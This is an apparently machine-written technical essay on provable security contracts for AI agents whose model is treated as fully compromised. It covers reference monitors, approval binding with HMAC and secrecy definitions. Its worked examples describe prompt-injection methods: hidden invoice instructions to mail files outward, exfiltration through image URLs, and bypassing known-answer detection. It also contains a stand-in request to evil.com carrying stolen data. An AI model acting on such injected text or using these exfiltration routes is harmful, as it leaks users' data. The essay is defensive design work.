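# Formal security guarantees for AI agent systems whose model may be fully compromised

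## What a security guarantee for an agent system claims

An AI agent system joins a language model to ordinary software that stores data and carries out actions. The model receives a request in plain language, picks a tool such as an email search or a payment service, receives the result, and picks again until the task is complete. A program called the driving loop passes text between the model and the tools. A formal security guarantee for such a system is a precise statement of something that cannot happen, even when an attacker controls the model. A contract lists the guarantees for one system and the conditions they depend on, so that somebody outside the project can check them.

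Ma and Schmid (2026), in *SecureClaw*, explain their design for such a system with a small office task. An assistant reads an invoice from vendor A, for $4,200 and due Friday, and emails it to an approver at approver@corp.com. Suppose somebody has added a line to the invoice, in white text on a white page, telling the assistant to send the invoice and the rest of the folder to an outside address, then finish the job as normal. A clerk who opens the file won't see the line, but the model receives it with the rest of the text.

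### How a model comes to follow an invoice

Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. A language model takes in a single sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and computes what should come next. The operator's instructions, the user's request and the text of the invoice are all in that sequence. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (Bhattarai and Vu, 2026) points out that the same learned function processes all of it, and that the markers separating "system" text from "user" text are themselves tokens, which an attacker can type. The input therefore has no unforgeable record of where a sentence came from. Database designers fixed a similar flaw by sending the command and the user's data through separate channels, so that no string in the data can turn into a command, but a typical agent has only one channel.

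Training can teach a model to ignore many planted instructions, but not every new instruction, since much of an agent's usefulness comes from picking up instructions as it works. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an agent that is asked to summarise an issue on a software project's page, finds that the issue depends on another one, and summarises both. Tool documentation is also meant to change an agent's behaviour. The wording of an instruction often doesn't show whether it is legitimate. For example, "Please copy our accounts office" may be a normal request or an attempt to steal information, depending on whose office it is.

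Bhattarai and Vu state a theorem that if a system separates commands from data only by their content, some attacker-written text has a non-zero probability of being treated as a command. Their proof sketch more or less assumes, rather than derives, that every learned boundary misclassifies some such text. The assumption is very plausible for language models. An engineer doesn't need the theorem, because nobody can put an upper bound on how often text that an attacker has had time to refine will succeed against a given model. Christodorescu and colleagues describe eleven attacks on real agent products, including Microsoft Copilot and Claude Code, and stress that the attackers needed no sophisticated tools.

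The engineer plans for full corruption, where the attacker chooses everything the model and its driving loop output, within the interfaces open to those components. In Ma and Schmid's version, the corrupted side can invent requests, change recipients, replay old approvals, mix up sessions and try to guess secret references. This assumption is deliberately pessimistic, and it covers a hidden instruction in an invoice, a bug in the loop, and a model with hostile aims of its own. It also means that a guarantee still holds after the model is replaced.

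### The reference monitor and the trusted core

The plan is much older than language models. In the early 1970s, the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), the report of an expert panel, identified the hard case as a malicious user with a legitimate account, who could write and run any program. The panel proposed controlling what any program could reach, rather than trying to work out which programs were malicious. Very little of the argument changes if the malicious user's program is replaced by a model that has processed a malicious invoice.

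The controlling component is a reference monitor, a trusted program that allows or denies every protected operation. Anderson required that nobody be able to tamper with it, that the system always invoke it, and that it be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Anderson's report assessed a commercial Honeywell system of the day against these requirements. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but the operating system suspended that check while working on the user's behalf, so the system did not always invoke the monitor. The operating system itself did not qualify as the monitor either, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were too many to analyse completely.

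Three years later, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* gave the requirement of constant checking its usual name, complete mediation. They extended it to start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance, and cautioned against relying on the results of earlier checks, because permissions change. In a contract for an agent, complete mediation is the assumption that no protected read or action can avoid the monitor. This assumption is easy to break by accident. If the machine that runs the driving loop also has the email password in a settings file, an attacker can bypass even a flawless monitor.

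The trusted core, which older literature calls the trusted computing base, consists of every component that must behave correctly for a guarantee to hold. That includes the monitor and whatever it relies on, such as the store that holds the invoice. In many agent products, the core also includes the model, because the designers rely on it to refuse bad instructions. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a hypothetical monitor that denies unauthorised access 99% of the time. If attempts were independent, an attacker who made a hundred of them would have about a 63% chance of getting through at least once. Real attempts aren't independent, which is worse for the defender, since an attacker can reuse a text that works. SecureClaw keeps the model outside its core, which contains only conventional software (a gateway, a data store, a policy engine and an executor).

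### A guarantee and a measured attack rate

A formal security guarantee always states that, under certain assumptions, no attacker of a specified kind can make a specified event happen. In the main theorem of Ma and Schmid, the attacker is any efficient program that can ask for approvals and submit actions, choosing each move after seeing the results of earlier ones. The theorem makes eight assumptions, including that every action with an outside effect passes through the executor. Under these assumptions, the executor never accepts an action without an approval, an altered version of an approved action, or the same approval twice.

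"Never" has some small print, which the theorem writes out as a bound:

Pr[attacker wins] ≤ Adv(forgery) + ε(collision)

The forgery term is the chance of faking an authentication code without the secret key. The collision term is the chance that two different requests have the same digital fingerprint. SecureClaw computes its fingerprints with HMAC-SHA256, a standard keyed function with a 256-bit output. Under the usual view of that function, the collision term would stay below one in 10^50 even after a trillion requests. Apart from these two terms, the claim that something "never" happens depends on the assumptions.

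Ma and Schmid also measured how often attacks on SecureClaw succeed, which is a different kind of result from a guarantee. They used two sets of scripted tasks with planted attacks, AgentDojo and Agent Security Bench, and ran them with gpt-4o-mini, a small model from July 2024. The attacks succeeded in 4 of 629 cases on AgentDojo and in 0 of 2,000 on Agent Security Bench. The 95% confidence interval for the second result reaches up to 0.18%, or about one success in 550. That interval covers only further attacks of the kind in the benchmark, and a real attacker can use other kinds.

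A defence's result on one benchmark can be a poor guide to its result on another, as the figures for SecureClaw's rivals show. DRIFT, which applies its rules inside the agent's own loop, let through 2.4% of the attacks on AgentDojo and 87.8% of those on Agent Security Bench. For IPIGuard, the figures were 15.3% and 99.6%. Ma and Schmid ran these rivals through their own adapters, so the comparison with SecureClaw deserves some caution, but the adapters are unlikely to account for such large differences within a single defence.

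Anderson discussed "tiger teams", groups of experts hired to break into a system, and observed that when a team fails, the system's security is still unknown. The reason, according to Saltzer and Schroeder, is that security is a negative requirement, meaning that a system must prevent every unauthorised use, including those that nobody thought to try. A proof covers the untried attacks by quantifying over all of them. Bhattarai and Vu prove, for their own design, that no sequence of model outputs can cause an action that the monitor's rule denies.

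Attack success rates count some failures that the theorems don't cover. All four of the successful AgentDojo attacks used actions that SecureClaw's policy permitted. In three, the action targeted the wrong person or lacked a link to its context, and in the fourth, a permitted change was made to the wrong object. These are policy-allowed errors, meaning actions that the policy permits but the user did not want. The theorem holds in all four cases but does not prevent the errors. Bhattarai and Vu make the same distinction between authorisation security, which rules out forbidden actions, and overall safety, which would rule out all harm. If the invoice assistant's policy lets it email anyone at corp.com, a hijacked model can send the invoice to the wrong colleague without violating any guarantee.

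### What a monitor can enforce

Some guarantees are impossible for any monitor to provide, however well it is built. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, treat a run of a program as an infinite sequence of states and a property as a set of runs. A safety property rules out some "bad thing". Formally, if a run violates the property, it does so by some finite point, after which no continuation can repair the damage. "No email goes to an address that the policy engine did not approve" is a safety property, since the violation is observable as soon as the email is sent. A liveness property requires some "good thing" to happen eventually, and any finite sequence of states can be extended to a run that satisfies it. "The approver eventually receives the invoice" is a liveness property, since the invoice may still arrive however long the approver has waited.

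Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) proved that a monitor which watches a system step by step, and halts it before a violation, can enforce only safety properties. One of its examples is the rule that a program may send no message after it has read a file. The monitor needs two states, "no file read" and "file read", and refuses every send in the second. Applied to the invoice assistant, this rule would stop the hidden instruction, but it would also stop the assistant from doing its job, which is to read a file and then send it. A useful contract therefore needs a finer rule about which messages may go where.

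A fully corrupted model can always do nothing, and no monitor can make it send an invoice. Adding a deadline doesn't solve this. "The approver receives the invoice within an hour" is a safety property, because a violation is visible once the hour is up, but the monitor can't prevent the violation because it can't stop time from passing. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, by Basin, Jugé and colleagues, refines Schneider's result to cover such cases by separating the actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe. To guarantee delivery, the designer would have to assign it to a trusted component.

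Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property is the combination of a safety property and a liveness property. In "The approver gets the invoice and nobody else does", the first half is a liveness property and the second half is a safety property. Only the second half can be guaranteed when the model is corrupted. A system that does nothing satisfies every safety property, so a safety guarantee is no evidence that a system is useful. On Agent Security Bench, both SecureClaw and a rival, Faramesh, reduced successful attacks to zero, but in Ma and Schmid's runs SecureClaw completed 88.9% of the tasks under attack and Faramesh completed 3.7%.

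### Secrecy needs two runs

Secrecy doesn't fit this scheme because it depends on comparing different runs. *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) gives the classic definition, called noninterference. A group of users does not interfere with an observer if, for every possible sequence of commands by all users, removing the group's commands and running the rest doesn't change what the observer sees at the end.

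Suppose the accounts department stores vendor A's invoice, and an outsider then asks the assistant for its status and is told "ready". In the comparison run, the department does nothing and the outsider asks the same question. If the reply is again "ready", this pair of runs shows no leak. If the reply was "one invoice pending" in the run with the invoice and "ready" in the run without it, noninterference fails, even though the outsider saw none of the invoice's contents. Goguen and Meseguer delete commands to get the comparison run, but to protect an invoice's contents, one can vary the secret instead. One run has an invoice for $4,200, the other has one for $9,900, and everything the observer receives must match. Ma and Schmid set up their secrecy proof this way, with the corrupted model's side as the observer trying to tell two stored values apart.

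A monitor that watches one run has no other run to compare it with. Schneider also notes that blocking additional runs can never break a safety property but can break secrecy. For example, a monitor that blocks the email whenever the invoice exceeds $5,000 creates a leak itself, because anyone who can see whether an email went out learns whether the invoice exceeds that amount.

In practice, a system can enforce a stricter safety property that implies the desired secrecy, for example that the raw invoice never enters the model's side. SecureClaw's gateway keeps the invoice and gives the model a handle, an unguessable reference to it. Full noninterference would hide even the amount and due date from the model, so the gateway also releases a short summary. The guarantee covers only the invoice information that the summary doesn't reveal.

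### The four parts of a contract

A complete contract states the guarantees, the boundary between trusted and untrusted components, the assumptions behind each guarantee, and what is lost when an attacker takes over a trusted component. A short version for the invoice assistant could read as follows.

| Part | Entry for the invoice assistant |
|---|---|
| Guarantees | **Actions:** whatever the untrusted side outputs, no email leaves unless the policy engine approved that exact request (recipient, channel, invoice version), and each approval works once. **Data:** whatever the untrusted side outputs, it learns nothing about the stored invoice beyond the declared releases, which are a handle, routine metadata, approve-or-deny answers and a short summary. |
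| Boundary | **Untrusted:** the model and its driving loop. **Trusted core:** gateway, data store, policy engine, executor. The untrusted side can request a read, propose an email and submit an approved request. It has no other route to the invoice or the email service. |
| Assumptions | **For actions:** only the executor can reach the email service; attackers cannot forge approvals; the approved request includes every field that affects what goes out; the record of used approvals survives a crash. **For data:** every read of an invoice passes through the gateway; the operator has marked the sensitive fields correctly; handles are too long to guess. |
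| Losses under compromise | **Executor:** the action guarantee fails, since the attacker then holds the connection to the email service. **Data store:** the data guarantee fails, since the attacker can read the invoice directly. |

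## Drawing the trust boundary and modelling the untrusted side

The boundary entry in the invoice assistant's contract is only a few lines long, but justifying it takes a fair amount of work. An engineer first lists the components, the protected data and the sinks, which are the interfaces where a request takes effect outside the system. The engineer then marks who can write to each item and who can call it, and only after that declares each component corruptible or trusted. The declarations come last because the marks often contradict what people assume, for example that the database is trusted.

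### Taking the inventory

The email service is an obvious sink, but the user's screen can be one too if it loads images from the web. A hijacked model can write the invoice amount into an image address, and the attacker's server receives the amount when the image loads. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, therefore has to assume that showing the user a reply has no effect an attacker can see. A tool that takes no arguments can also be a sink, as Ma and Schmid point out, and a defence that inspects arguments has nothing to inspect there. The agent's memory and its messages to other agents are usually on the untrusted side, so the engineer should treat whatever reaches them as known to the attacker.

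Recording who can write to each component separates trust in the component from trust in its contents. Vendor A writes the invoice, so the text may be hostile even if the data store stores it without alteration. Dongol gives the example of a user's own calendar, which is not a trusted source if it accepts invitations from outsiders. The defence's own files need the same check, because a driving loop that can edit the policy file can change what the policy permits.

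Working out who can call what mostly means finding credentials. *AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) describes a security layer that an agent reaches through separate adapters for the model, the tools and storage. It lists ways an agent could bypass them, such as credentials left in its environment, a direct connection to a tool, or a file path that avoids the storage adapter.

With the marks in place, the engineer can usually see which components a guarantee relies on and leave the rest corruptible. The difficult case is a component that both processes the attacker's text and holds something valuable. In a typical agent, the driving loop does both, because it passes the invoice to the model and has the email password. The usual remedy is to split the component, and SecureClaw's design largely results from such a split.

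| Component | What it holds | Who can call it | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model and driving loop | The user's request, handles, summaries, its own memory | The user | Corruptible |
| Gateway | The rules for recognising sensitive fields; the keys for making handles and request fingerprints | The untrusted side | Trusted |
| Data store | The raw invoice and the record behind each handle | Gateway, executor | Trusted |
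| Policy engine | The policy; the key for authenticating approvals | Gateway | Trusted |
| Executor | The connection to the email service; the record of used approvals; the keys for checking fingerprints and approvals | The untrusted side | Trusted |

Ma and Schmid call the untrusted side "the runtime", which is confusing because other authors use that word for trusted code. The untrusted side can call only the gateway and the executor, so their interfaces make up most of the trust boundary.

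### The invoice on its way in

When the assistant asks for vendor A's invoice, the gateway receives the file and checks its fields against the rules for sensitive data. It puts the raw text in the data store and makes a handle, for which Ma and Schmid suggest this formula:

handle = HMAC-SHA256(handle key, nonce ‖ session ‖ object)

The nonce is a value the gateway uses only once, and the bars mean that the gateway joins the three items together. The formula doesn't include the invoice's text, so an attacker who suspects the amount is $4,200 can't test that guess against the handle. The data store records who may use the handle, in which session, until when, for which version of the invoice and for which destinations.

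The gateway also returns a short summary, such as "vendor A, amount $4.2k, due Friday", written by a fixed program that doesn't call a language model. The program keeps at most eight fields or list items per container and cuts each text field at 512 characters. It replaces email addresses, account numbers and web addresses with new tokens on each read, and removes suspicious markers that are on a configured list. Some planted instructions will still reach the model. For example, the program can't distinguish an instruction written in ordinary words near the start of a free-text field from other text. The design tolerates this because it already treats the model as hostile.

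### The email on its way out

The model now proposes to send the invoice, which it knows only by its handle, to approver@corp.com. In the preview step, the gateway turns this proposal into a complete request with five parts: the type of action, the caller, the session, the inputs and the context. The model supplies the type of action and the inputs. The gateway adds the caller and session from its own authenticated records, together with context such as the invoice version. It then writes the whole request out in a fixed format, so that the same request always produces the same bytes, and computes a fingerprint:

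h = HMAC-SHA256(binding key, Canon(request))

Canon stands for the fixed format. Before any email is sent, the policy engine checks the request against its rules and returns an approval containing h, the decision and a timestamp, with an authentication code over all three.

In the commit step, the executor receives the request and the approval and recomputes h itself, because the request may have passed through the untrusted side since the preview. If the attacker has changed the recipient to an outside address, the new fingerprint doesn't match the one in the approval and the executor refuses. It also checks that the approval is genuine, recent and unused, and that the handle's record permits this destination. For actions that also need the user's confirmation, it checks that the confirmation belongs to this exact request. The executor looks up the raw invoice and calls the email service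 only after all these checks pass.

A refusal also crosses the trust boundary, because it goes back to the untrusted side. The executor picks it from a fixed set of templates, which contain a broad action class, a reason code and a hint like saving a draft instead. A more helpful message, such as one that quoted the invoice, would leak information.

### The attacker as a program that asks questions

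Before anyone can prove a theorem about full corruption, it needs a mathematical form, and the published forms don't all cover the same attackers.

Ma and Schmid use the standard form from cryptography, a game in which the attacker program from their main theorem sends queries to two interfaces, preview and commit. The game contains no language model. Whatever a hijacked model could achieve through those interfaces, some program could also achieve, so a bound on what any program can achieve covers the model too. The program has to be efficient, because one with unlimited time could try every possible key.

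This attacker is stronger than a real one in that it gives the preview interface a complete request, including the caller and session, which the gateway would fill in during deployment. The theorem therefore holds even if the attacker lies about who is calling, but it doesn't show that the gateway identifies callers correctly. If the gateway mistook an intern for the finance director, and the policy let the director send the invoice, the email would count as authorised.

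This form leaves out every interaction that isn't a query to one of the listed interfaces. The game doesn't cover a forgotten second route to the email service, so the proof must assume complete mediation to rule it out. Smaller gaps are easier to miss, such as when the commit interface in the game returns only "accept" or "deny" but the deployed executor also returns a reason code. The reason code probably doesn't help anyone forge an approval, but that still has to be argued.

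### The attacker as an arbitrary value

*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) uses havoc, a program-verification technique that gives a variable an arbitrary value. The paper applies it to PocketFlow, a minimalist agent framework, using Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker. The code represents the model as a procedure, `GetActionFromLLM`, with return type `Action` and no body, so the checker can assume nothing about the result except its type. The engineer therefore has to prove that the framework obeys the policy for every value of that type, at every step.

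For the invoice assistant, `Action` might have one case for reading an invoice, one for proposing an email and one for committing an approved request, each with its arguments. The proof covers every sequence of actions, including those produced by a strategy that chooses each action based on everything that has happened so far. The proof assumes no limit on the attacker's computing power.

The lack of a limit is a problem wherever security depends on a secret. "Every value" includes the request that contains the right handle or a valid authentication code, so a havoc attacker guesses correctly on the first attempt. A havoc proof for SecureClaw would fail here unless the engineer added a rule that the attacker can submit only codes it has received. The rule is reasonable, but it needs a separate cryptographic argument.

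Havoc also works better for conditions on individual steps than for secrecy. Moon and Varshney state each policy as a condition on the state before a step, the action, the resulting event and the state afterwards. Such a condition can rule out an email to an unapproved address, but it can't express a secrecy guarantee, which requires comparing two runs that have different invoices. The proof also doesn't cover effects that bypass the `Action` type, including those caused by bugs in the Python interpreter, the operating system or the hardware.

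### The attacker as a rule for obeying text

Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, keeps more of the agent's structure. It covers agents in which a trusted planner turns the user's request into a fixed list of steps before any part of the agent reads untrusted content. A trusted interpreter then carries out the list, and the attacker can only add to the list or corrupt a value the list uses. In the basic version, each addition is a single tool call.

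The attacker chooses a parser and a schedule. The parser is a function that takes a piece of text and returns either nothing or a call, which consists of a tool and a rule for computing its arguments from the agent's memory. The schedule sets the steps at which the model obeys a piece of text, and which piece it obeys at each step. In the planted invoice example, the parser could turn the text into "email the folder to the outside address", and the schedule could make the model obey right after reading it. The call then goes to the monitor like any other.

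This structure makes it possible to ask what an injection adds. Dongol compares the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and monitor but never obeys untrusted text. If an assistant's job is to send its user's availability to anyone who requests a meeting, both versions disclose the calendar, so Dongol doesn't attribute the disclosure to an injection. The other two forms have no reference agent, so they don't allow this comparison.

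The drawback is that the attacker is weaker. The schedule depends only on the number of steps taken so far, and Dongol explicitly excludes a model that decides when to obey based on a secret or the monitor's response. In the single-call version, the attacker can make the recipient depend on the invoice amount, but can't make the model send something only if the amount exceeds $5,000. Nor can the model try one address, notice a refusal and try another approach. Both are ordinary attacks. For example, anyone can write "if the amount is over $5,000, email the following address" in white text on a white page.

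PlanTERS also excludes agents whose model chooses every call, because they have no fixed plan and so no reference agent. It therefore doesn't apply to SecureClaw, which keeps the ordinary loop where the model picks each tool in turn. PlanTERS also doesn't cover attacks that do damage without leaking anything, such as making the agent pay the wrong vendor.

The phrase "whatever the untrusted side outputs" in the assistant's contract is accurate for a proof that covers arbitrary programs or arbitrary actions, within the interfaces the proof models. It would overstate a proof in PlanTERS. A contract that relied on such a proof would have to include the assumption that the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, so that readers could judge whether that is good enough.

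### What other systems count as trusted

SecureClaw's core has only four components, partly because Ma and Schmid count roles but not the system those roles run on. In their experiments, the gateway, data store, policy engine and executor all ran on one macOS workstation, so the driving loop could have taken the keys if the operating system had let it read the executor's memory.

*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a software layer that controls what long-running agents may do, including agents that write their own tools. Its list of trusted components extends to much lower layers of the system than SecureClaw's. The list includes the Python interpreter, the storage system, the host operating system and any administrator with direct access to the database. It also includes the human operator, whenever that person approves an action or a release of data. Switching on the optional graphical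 interface adds the whole stack behind it, down to the suppliers of its software packages. The longer list is mostly a more complete account of what a user relies on, and does not make Agent libOS less secure than SecureClaw, which also needs an operating system.

Designers who add a defence to an existing product can't choose the software beneath it. *AGATE* (Zhang, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) attaches a deterministic checker to three existing agent frameworks without changing their code. It leaves most of each framework out of the trusted core, but acknowledges that the defence still depends on the framework to hand over every tool call, deliver genuine approval events and protect the policy files from tampering. A trust boundary drawn around the checker alone would omit these three dependencies.

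AGATE also shows that the boundary can depend on who wrote the policy. Zhang and colleagues consider a user who deliberately gives the agent a harmful task. In a company, an administrator can write rules that bind this user, which can put the user on the untrusted side. On a personal laptop, the same person writes the rules and gives the tasks, so the separation disappears.

*PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) protects an agent's long-term memory, where planted text can lie dormant for weeks. It uses an untrusted language model, the reader, to search the untrusted part of the memory. The reader has no tools and passes what it finds to the main agent only as handles. The secrecy-style proof compares two runs in which the reader's outputs may differ arbitrarily, so it holds however hostile the reader is. Jiang and colleagues define the trusted core as the fixed parts that no model output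 can alter, such as the interpreter and the code that displays values for approval.

PerMIT ultimately relies on a confirmation gate, where either a person or another language model sees an exact value and accepts or rejects it. The theorems assume that every accepted value is trustworthy.

AgentKernel deliberately includes a learned component in its trusted core. Incoming text passes through a source tagger and a set of pattern rules, and then a language model classifies it as acceptable or not, with stricter thresholds for less trusted sources. Zou and colleagues say that their core is not small. A guarantee that no planted instruction reaches the main model would depend completely on the classifier, but a guarantee that a tool can make only the system calls on a fixed list would rest on a separate check near the operating system. The trusted core is therefore worth drawing separately for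 each guarantee.

### Can a learned component be trusted?

Bhattarai and Vu's trusted core has a parser, a policy engine, a component that labels data and checks its flow, tool adapters and a log, all of which must work without any language model. A learned guard that reads the same text as the agent is open to the same manipulation. They think better alignment wouldn't help, because even a model with perfect intentions can't verify who wrote a sentence. They also warn that errors add up in chains of agents. If each agent is right 94.3% of the time and errors are independent, a chain of ten is right about 56% of the time.

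Known-answer detection illustrates the problem with guards. The defender gives a second model the suspicious text along with an instruction to repeat a secret key. If the model doesn't repeat the key, the text has presumably hijacked it. Christodorescu and colleagues report that this worked nearly perfectly against existing attacks. Attackers then found text that makes the model both repeat the key and carry out the planted instruction. This was possible because the key and the text share one context.

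*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) takes the deterministic position to its extreme. It treats the model as a superhuman adversary that knows every rule, and uses a logic solver to check each action against fixed safety axioms before it happens. The paper describes its stance as pessimistic about the model and optimistic about the verifier. The guarantee depends heavily on that optimism, because the paper assumes the attacker can't bypass or alter the verifier. It also depends on the code that translates actions into logic. If that code omits an email's recipient, the solver's proof will be valid but won't cover who receives the email.

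Christodorescu and colleagues make the case for working on learned components, although they call it "perhaps impossible" to build provable defences on a probabilistic core. They list this as a long-term research problem because a deterministic monitor needs a policy, and for most agent tasks nobody has written one. Suppose a user types "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done". The right policy lets the agent open that issue and write in the comment box, and nothing else. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs a different policy. Developers can't anticipate these requests, and most users can't write security policies, so a language model is the obvious candidate to write them.

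Tracking where information goes raises a similar difficulty. When a model combines ten documents, a deterministic tracker has to assume that the output contains something from all ten, and soon every piece of data carries every label. A trustworthy tracker that understood the text could be more precise. To trust one, Christodorescu and colleagues would require it to be secure against adaptive attackers with unlimited computing power. They describe a partial approach that checks a model's decision against facts from outside the model. The SkillFence system does this for voice assistants, using a user's installed apps and visited websites to correct the assistant's misunderstandings.

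Bhattarai and Vu concede that good policies are very hard to design, and recommend that people write conservative ones and accept that some actions will be wrongly blocked. But people are unreliable too. One of their sample policies lets an agent read confidential files after a user confirms, and nobody has proved that users confirm only what they should. The best argument for relying on people anyway is probably that an attacker can test thousands of texts against a copy of a model, but not against a particular person. That is a reason to prefer human approvers, but it doesn't formally guarantee their decisions.

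Neither side has a learned component with a proven limit on its errors against an adaptive attacker, so a contract written today shouldn't depend on one to guarantee that something never happens. The monitor can still include a learned component that only adds refusals. In AgentKernel, an action needs permission from every applicable policy, so an extra policy can only shrink the set of allowed actions. A classifier added this way can't break a guarantee about actions, however badly it performs, though it could make the assistant useless. Secrecy needs more care because a refusal can itself leak information, as with the rule that blocks invoices above $5,000.

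A learned component that grants permission is much more dangerous. If a model writes the policy, marks the sensitive fields or approves values at a gate, its mistakes widen what an attacker can do. The engineer can put that model in the trusted core, but the guarantee is then statistical. Alternatively, the contract can guarantee only that no email leaves without permission from the policy in force, whoever or whatever wrote it. This is still provable, but it protects only as well as the policy does. PerMIT's theorems likewise still hold with a language model at the gate, because they assume that every approval is right. The evidence for that assumption is experimental. Jiang and colleagues observed no successful attacks on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which text planted in one session takes effect in a later one.

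## Stating what the agent can do

Once the boundary is in place, the engineer can state the guarantee in terms of the agent's actions. Published systems offer three forms of this guarantee, which differ mainly in who works out which actions are safe, and when. SecureClaw ties every action to an approval of that exact request. Alignment contracts set rules for the whole sequence of an agent's effects, such as a limit on the total number of requests. Proof-carrying contracts require the agent to submit a mathematical proof with every call.

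### An approval for one exact request

SecureClaw relies on message authentication codes. Such a code is a short tag that a program computes from a message and a secret key. Anyone else with the key can recompute the tag, and a match shows that a key holder produced it for exactly that message. Cryptographers require that an attacker who can get tags for any number of messages it chooses still be unable to produce a valid tag for any new message, even a meaningless one.

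Every approval from SecureClaw's policy engine carries such a tag and an identifier for the action. The tags and the fingerprints use different keys. If they shared a key, an attacker could try to submit a request whose bytes matched an approval record, then present the request's fingerprint as the record's tag.

Tags and fingerprints cover bytes, so the gateway and the executor must use the same fixed format, called a canonical serialization. If one put the recipient first and the other put the subject first, the executor would refuse legitimate emails. A format that produces the same bytes for two different requests is much worse. If the serialization just joined the recipient to the note, an email to approver@corp.co with the note "march invoice" and an email to approver@corp.com with the note "arch invoice" would both become "approver@corp.comarch invoice". An approval for one would then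 work for the other, which goes to a different company.

In the game behind Ma and Schmid's main theorem, the attacker wins if the executor ever accepts one of the following.

| What the executor accepts | Example | Premises that rule it out |
|---|---|---|
| An action with no matching approval | The model makes up an approval for an outside address | Attackers can't forge tags |
| A request that differs from the approved one, in its bytes or its effect | The model gets approval for approver@corp.com, then changes the recipient | Different requests get different fingerprints; both sides serialize identically; the serialization includes every field that can change the effect |
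| An approval that the executor has accepted before | The model submits one approved payment twice | The executor checks and marks each identifier in a single step, and the mark survives a crash |

The executor checks and marks a commit in a single step. If checking and marking were separate, two copies of the same commit that arrived together could both pass the check before the executor marked either one.

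The theorem also assumes three things that no winning condition covers: that the executor refuses expired approvals, that any required user confirmation belongs to this exact request, and that every action with an outside effect goes through the executor. For example, accepting an expired approval doesn't count as a win in the game, so the theorem is no evidence that the executor refuses one. A contract that promises that refusal needs a direct check of the executor's code.

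In the paper's notation, the bound from the first section reads:

Pr[win] ≤ Adv_MAC + ε_bind

These are the forgery and collision terms from before. The proof uses game hopping, a standard technique that changes the game in small steps and bounds how much each step can change the attacker's chances.

1. Game 0 is the real game.
2. Game 1 stops if the executor accepts a tag on a record that the policy engine never tagged. The two games are identical until that happens, so the attacker's chances differ by at most the probability of it happening. Whenever it does happen, the attacker has forged a tag, so this step costs at most Adv_MAC.
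3. Game 2 also stops if two requests with different bytes share a fingerprint. This step costs at most ε_bind.

The attacker can't win Game 2, because every commit the executor accepts has a genuine approval, the same bytes as the approved request, and a previously unused identifier. By the serialization premise, the same bytes have the same effect. The bound is the sum of the most that each of the two steps can change the attacker's probability of winning.

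The first section's figure for the collision term comes from counting pairs. A trillion requests, or about 2^40, produce about 2^79 pairs of fingerprints, and any two 256-bit fingerprints match with probability 2^-256, so the chance of any match is about 2^-177. An attacker submitting a million requests per second would need nearly two weeks to make that many requests. After a century at the same rate, the chance would still be only about 2^-154. The attacker can't speed up the search on its own hardware, because computing a fingerprint requires the secret key. If an engineer cut fingerprints to 64 bits to save space, however, the same 2^40 requests would produce about 32,000 matching pairs.

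### Equal bytes and equal effects

The cryptography proves that the bytes at commit match the bytes at preview. The user cares about the email that goes out, and the proof covers that only under the premise that requests with equal bytes, sent to the same service, have equal effects. Ma and Schmid acknowledge that this premise, rather than the collision term, rules out equal bytes with different effects. So the theorem excludes half of its second winning condition by assumption.

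Taken literally, the premise is false for most services that have settings or data of their own. If a request names "vendor A's latest invoice", the vendor can upload another invoice between the approval and the email. SecureClaw prevents this by including version identifiers for objects that can change. But the change can also happen outside the system, where the engineer has no version number to include. If approver@corp.com is a mailing list, somebody can add a member after the approval. An email account may also be set to copy every message to another address.

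The system can partly remedy this before the preview by resolving anything that might later change, for example by replacing a mailing list with its current members. Where it can't, the contract can make the weaker claim that the email service receives exactly the request that the policy engine approved. The cryptography supports this claim, and what the service does afterwards becomes a separate assumption.

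This form of guarantee suits distinct actions that are hard to undo, such as payments and emails, especially when one component decides and another executes later. It works poorly for limits on the combined effect of many actions. The policy engine could keep a running count, but the theorem wouldn't guarantee that the count was right.

### Rules for the whole run

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) states the guarantee over the whole sequence of the agent's effects. In its example, a security firm sends an agent to look for weaknesses in a client's websites. The client's brief covers all subdomains of example.com and allows only GET and HEAD requests, which fetch a page or just its headers. It forbids the agent from accessing local files or starting other programs. The agent may send 10,000 requests in total, and its reports may go only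 to the operator's dashboard.

The monitor receives each attempted effect as an event, which records the class of effect (network, file or program), its parameters, the time and the agent's identifier. The events admitted so far form the trace. The monitor admits a new event only if it passes five clauses:

1. **Scope:** the target is in the contract's permitted set.
2. **Allowed:** the contract permits this type of effect.
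3. **Not forbidden:** the effect isn't on a list of prohibited effects, which overrides the permissions.
4. **Budget:** for each counted resource, the cost of this event plus the cost of the trace so far stays within the limit.
5. **Disclosure:** every declared flow of information goes to an approved destination.

David and colleagues apply the contract to six requests.

| Attempted request | Decision |
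|---|---|
| GET api.example.com/users | Admitted |
| HEAD login.example.com | Admitted |
| GET api.example.com/admin, which redirects to admin.example-corp.com | Admitted, since the requested host is in scope |
| GET admin.example-corp.com | Refused: out of scope |
| POST api.example.com/login, with an attack on the site's database | Refused: POST isn't an allowed method |
| GET evil.com/collect, with stolen data attached | Refused: out of scope |

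The last request comes from a hidden comment on one of the client's pages, which tells the agent to send its findings to evil.com. The monitor refuses the request because of its destination, so it doesn't have to detect the injection.

Refused requests don't count towards the budget, so the agent has used 3 of its 10,000. Once the monitor has admitted 10,000 requests, it refuses the next. The brief sets no limit on speed, so a hijacked agent could send all 10,000 within a minute and perhaps overload the site. The core language can't express a limit per minute, which David and colleagues leave as an extension.

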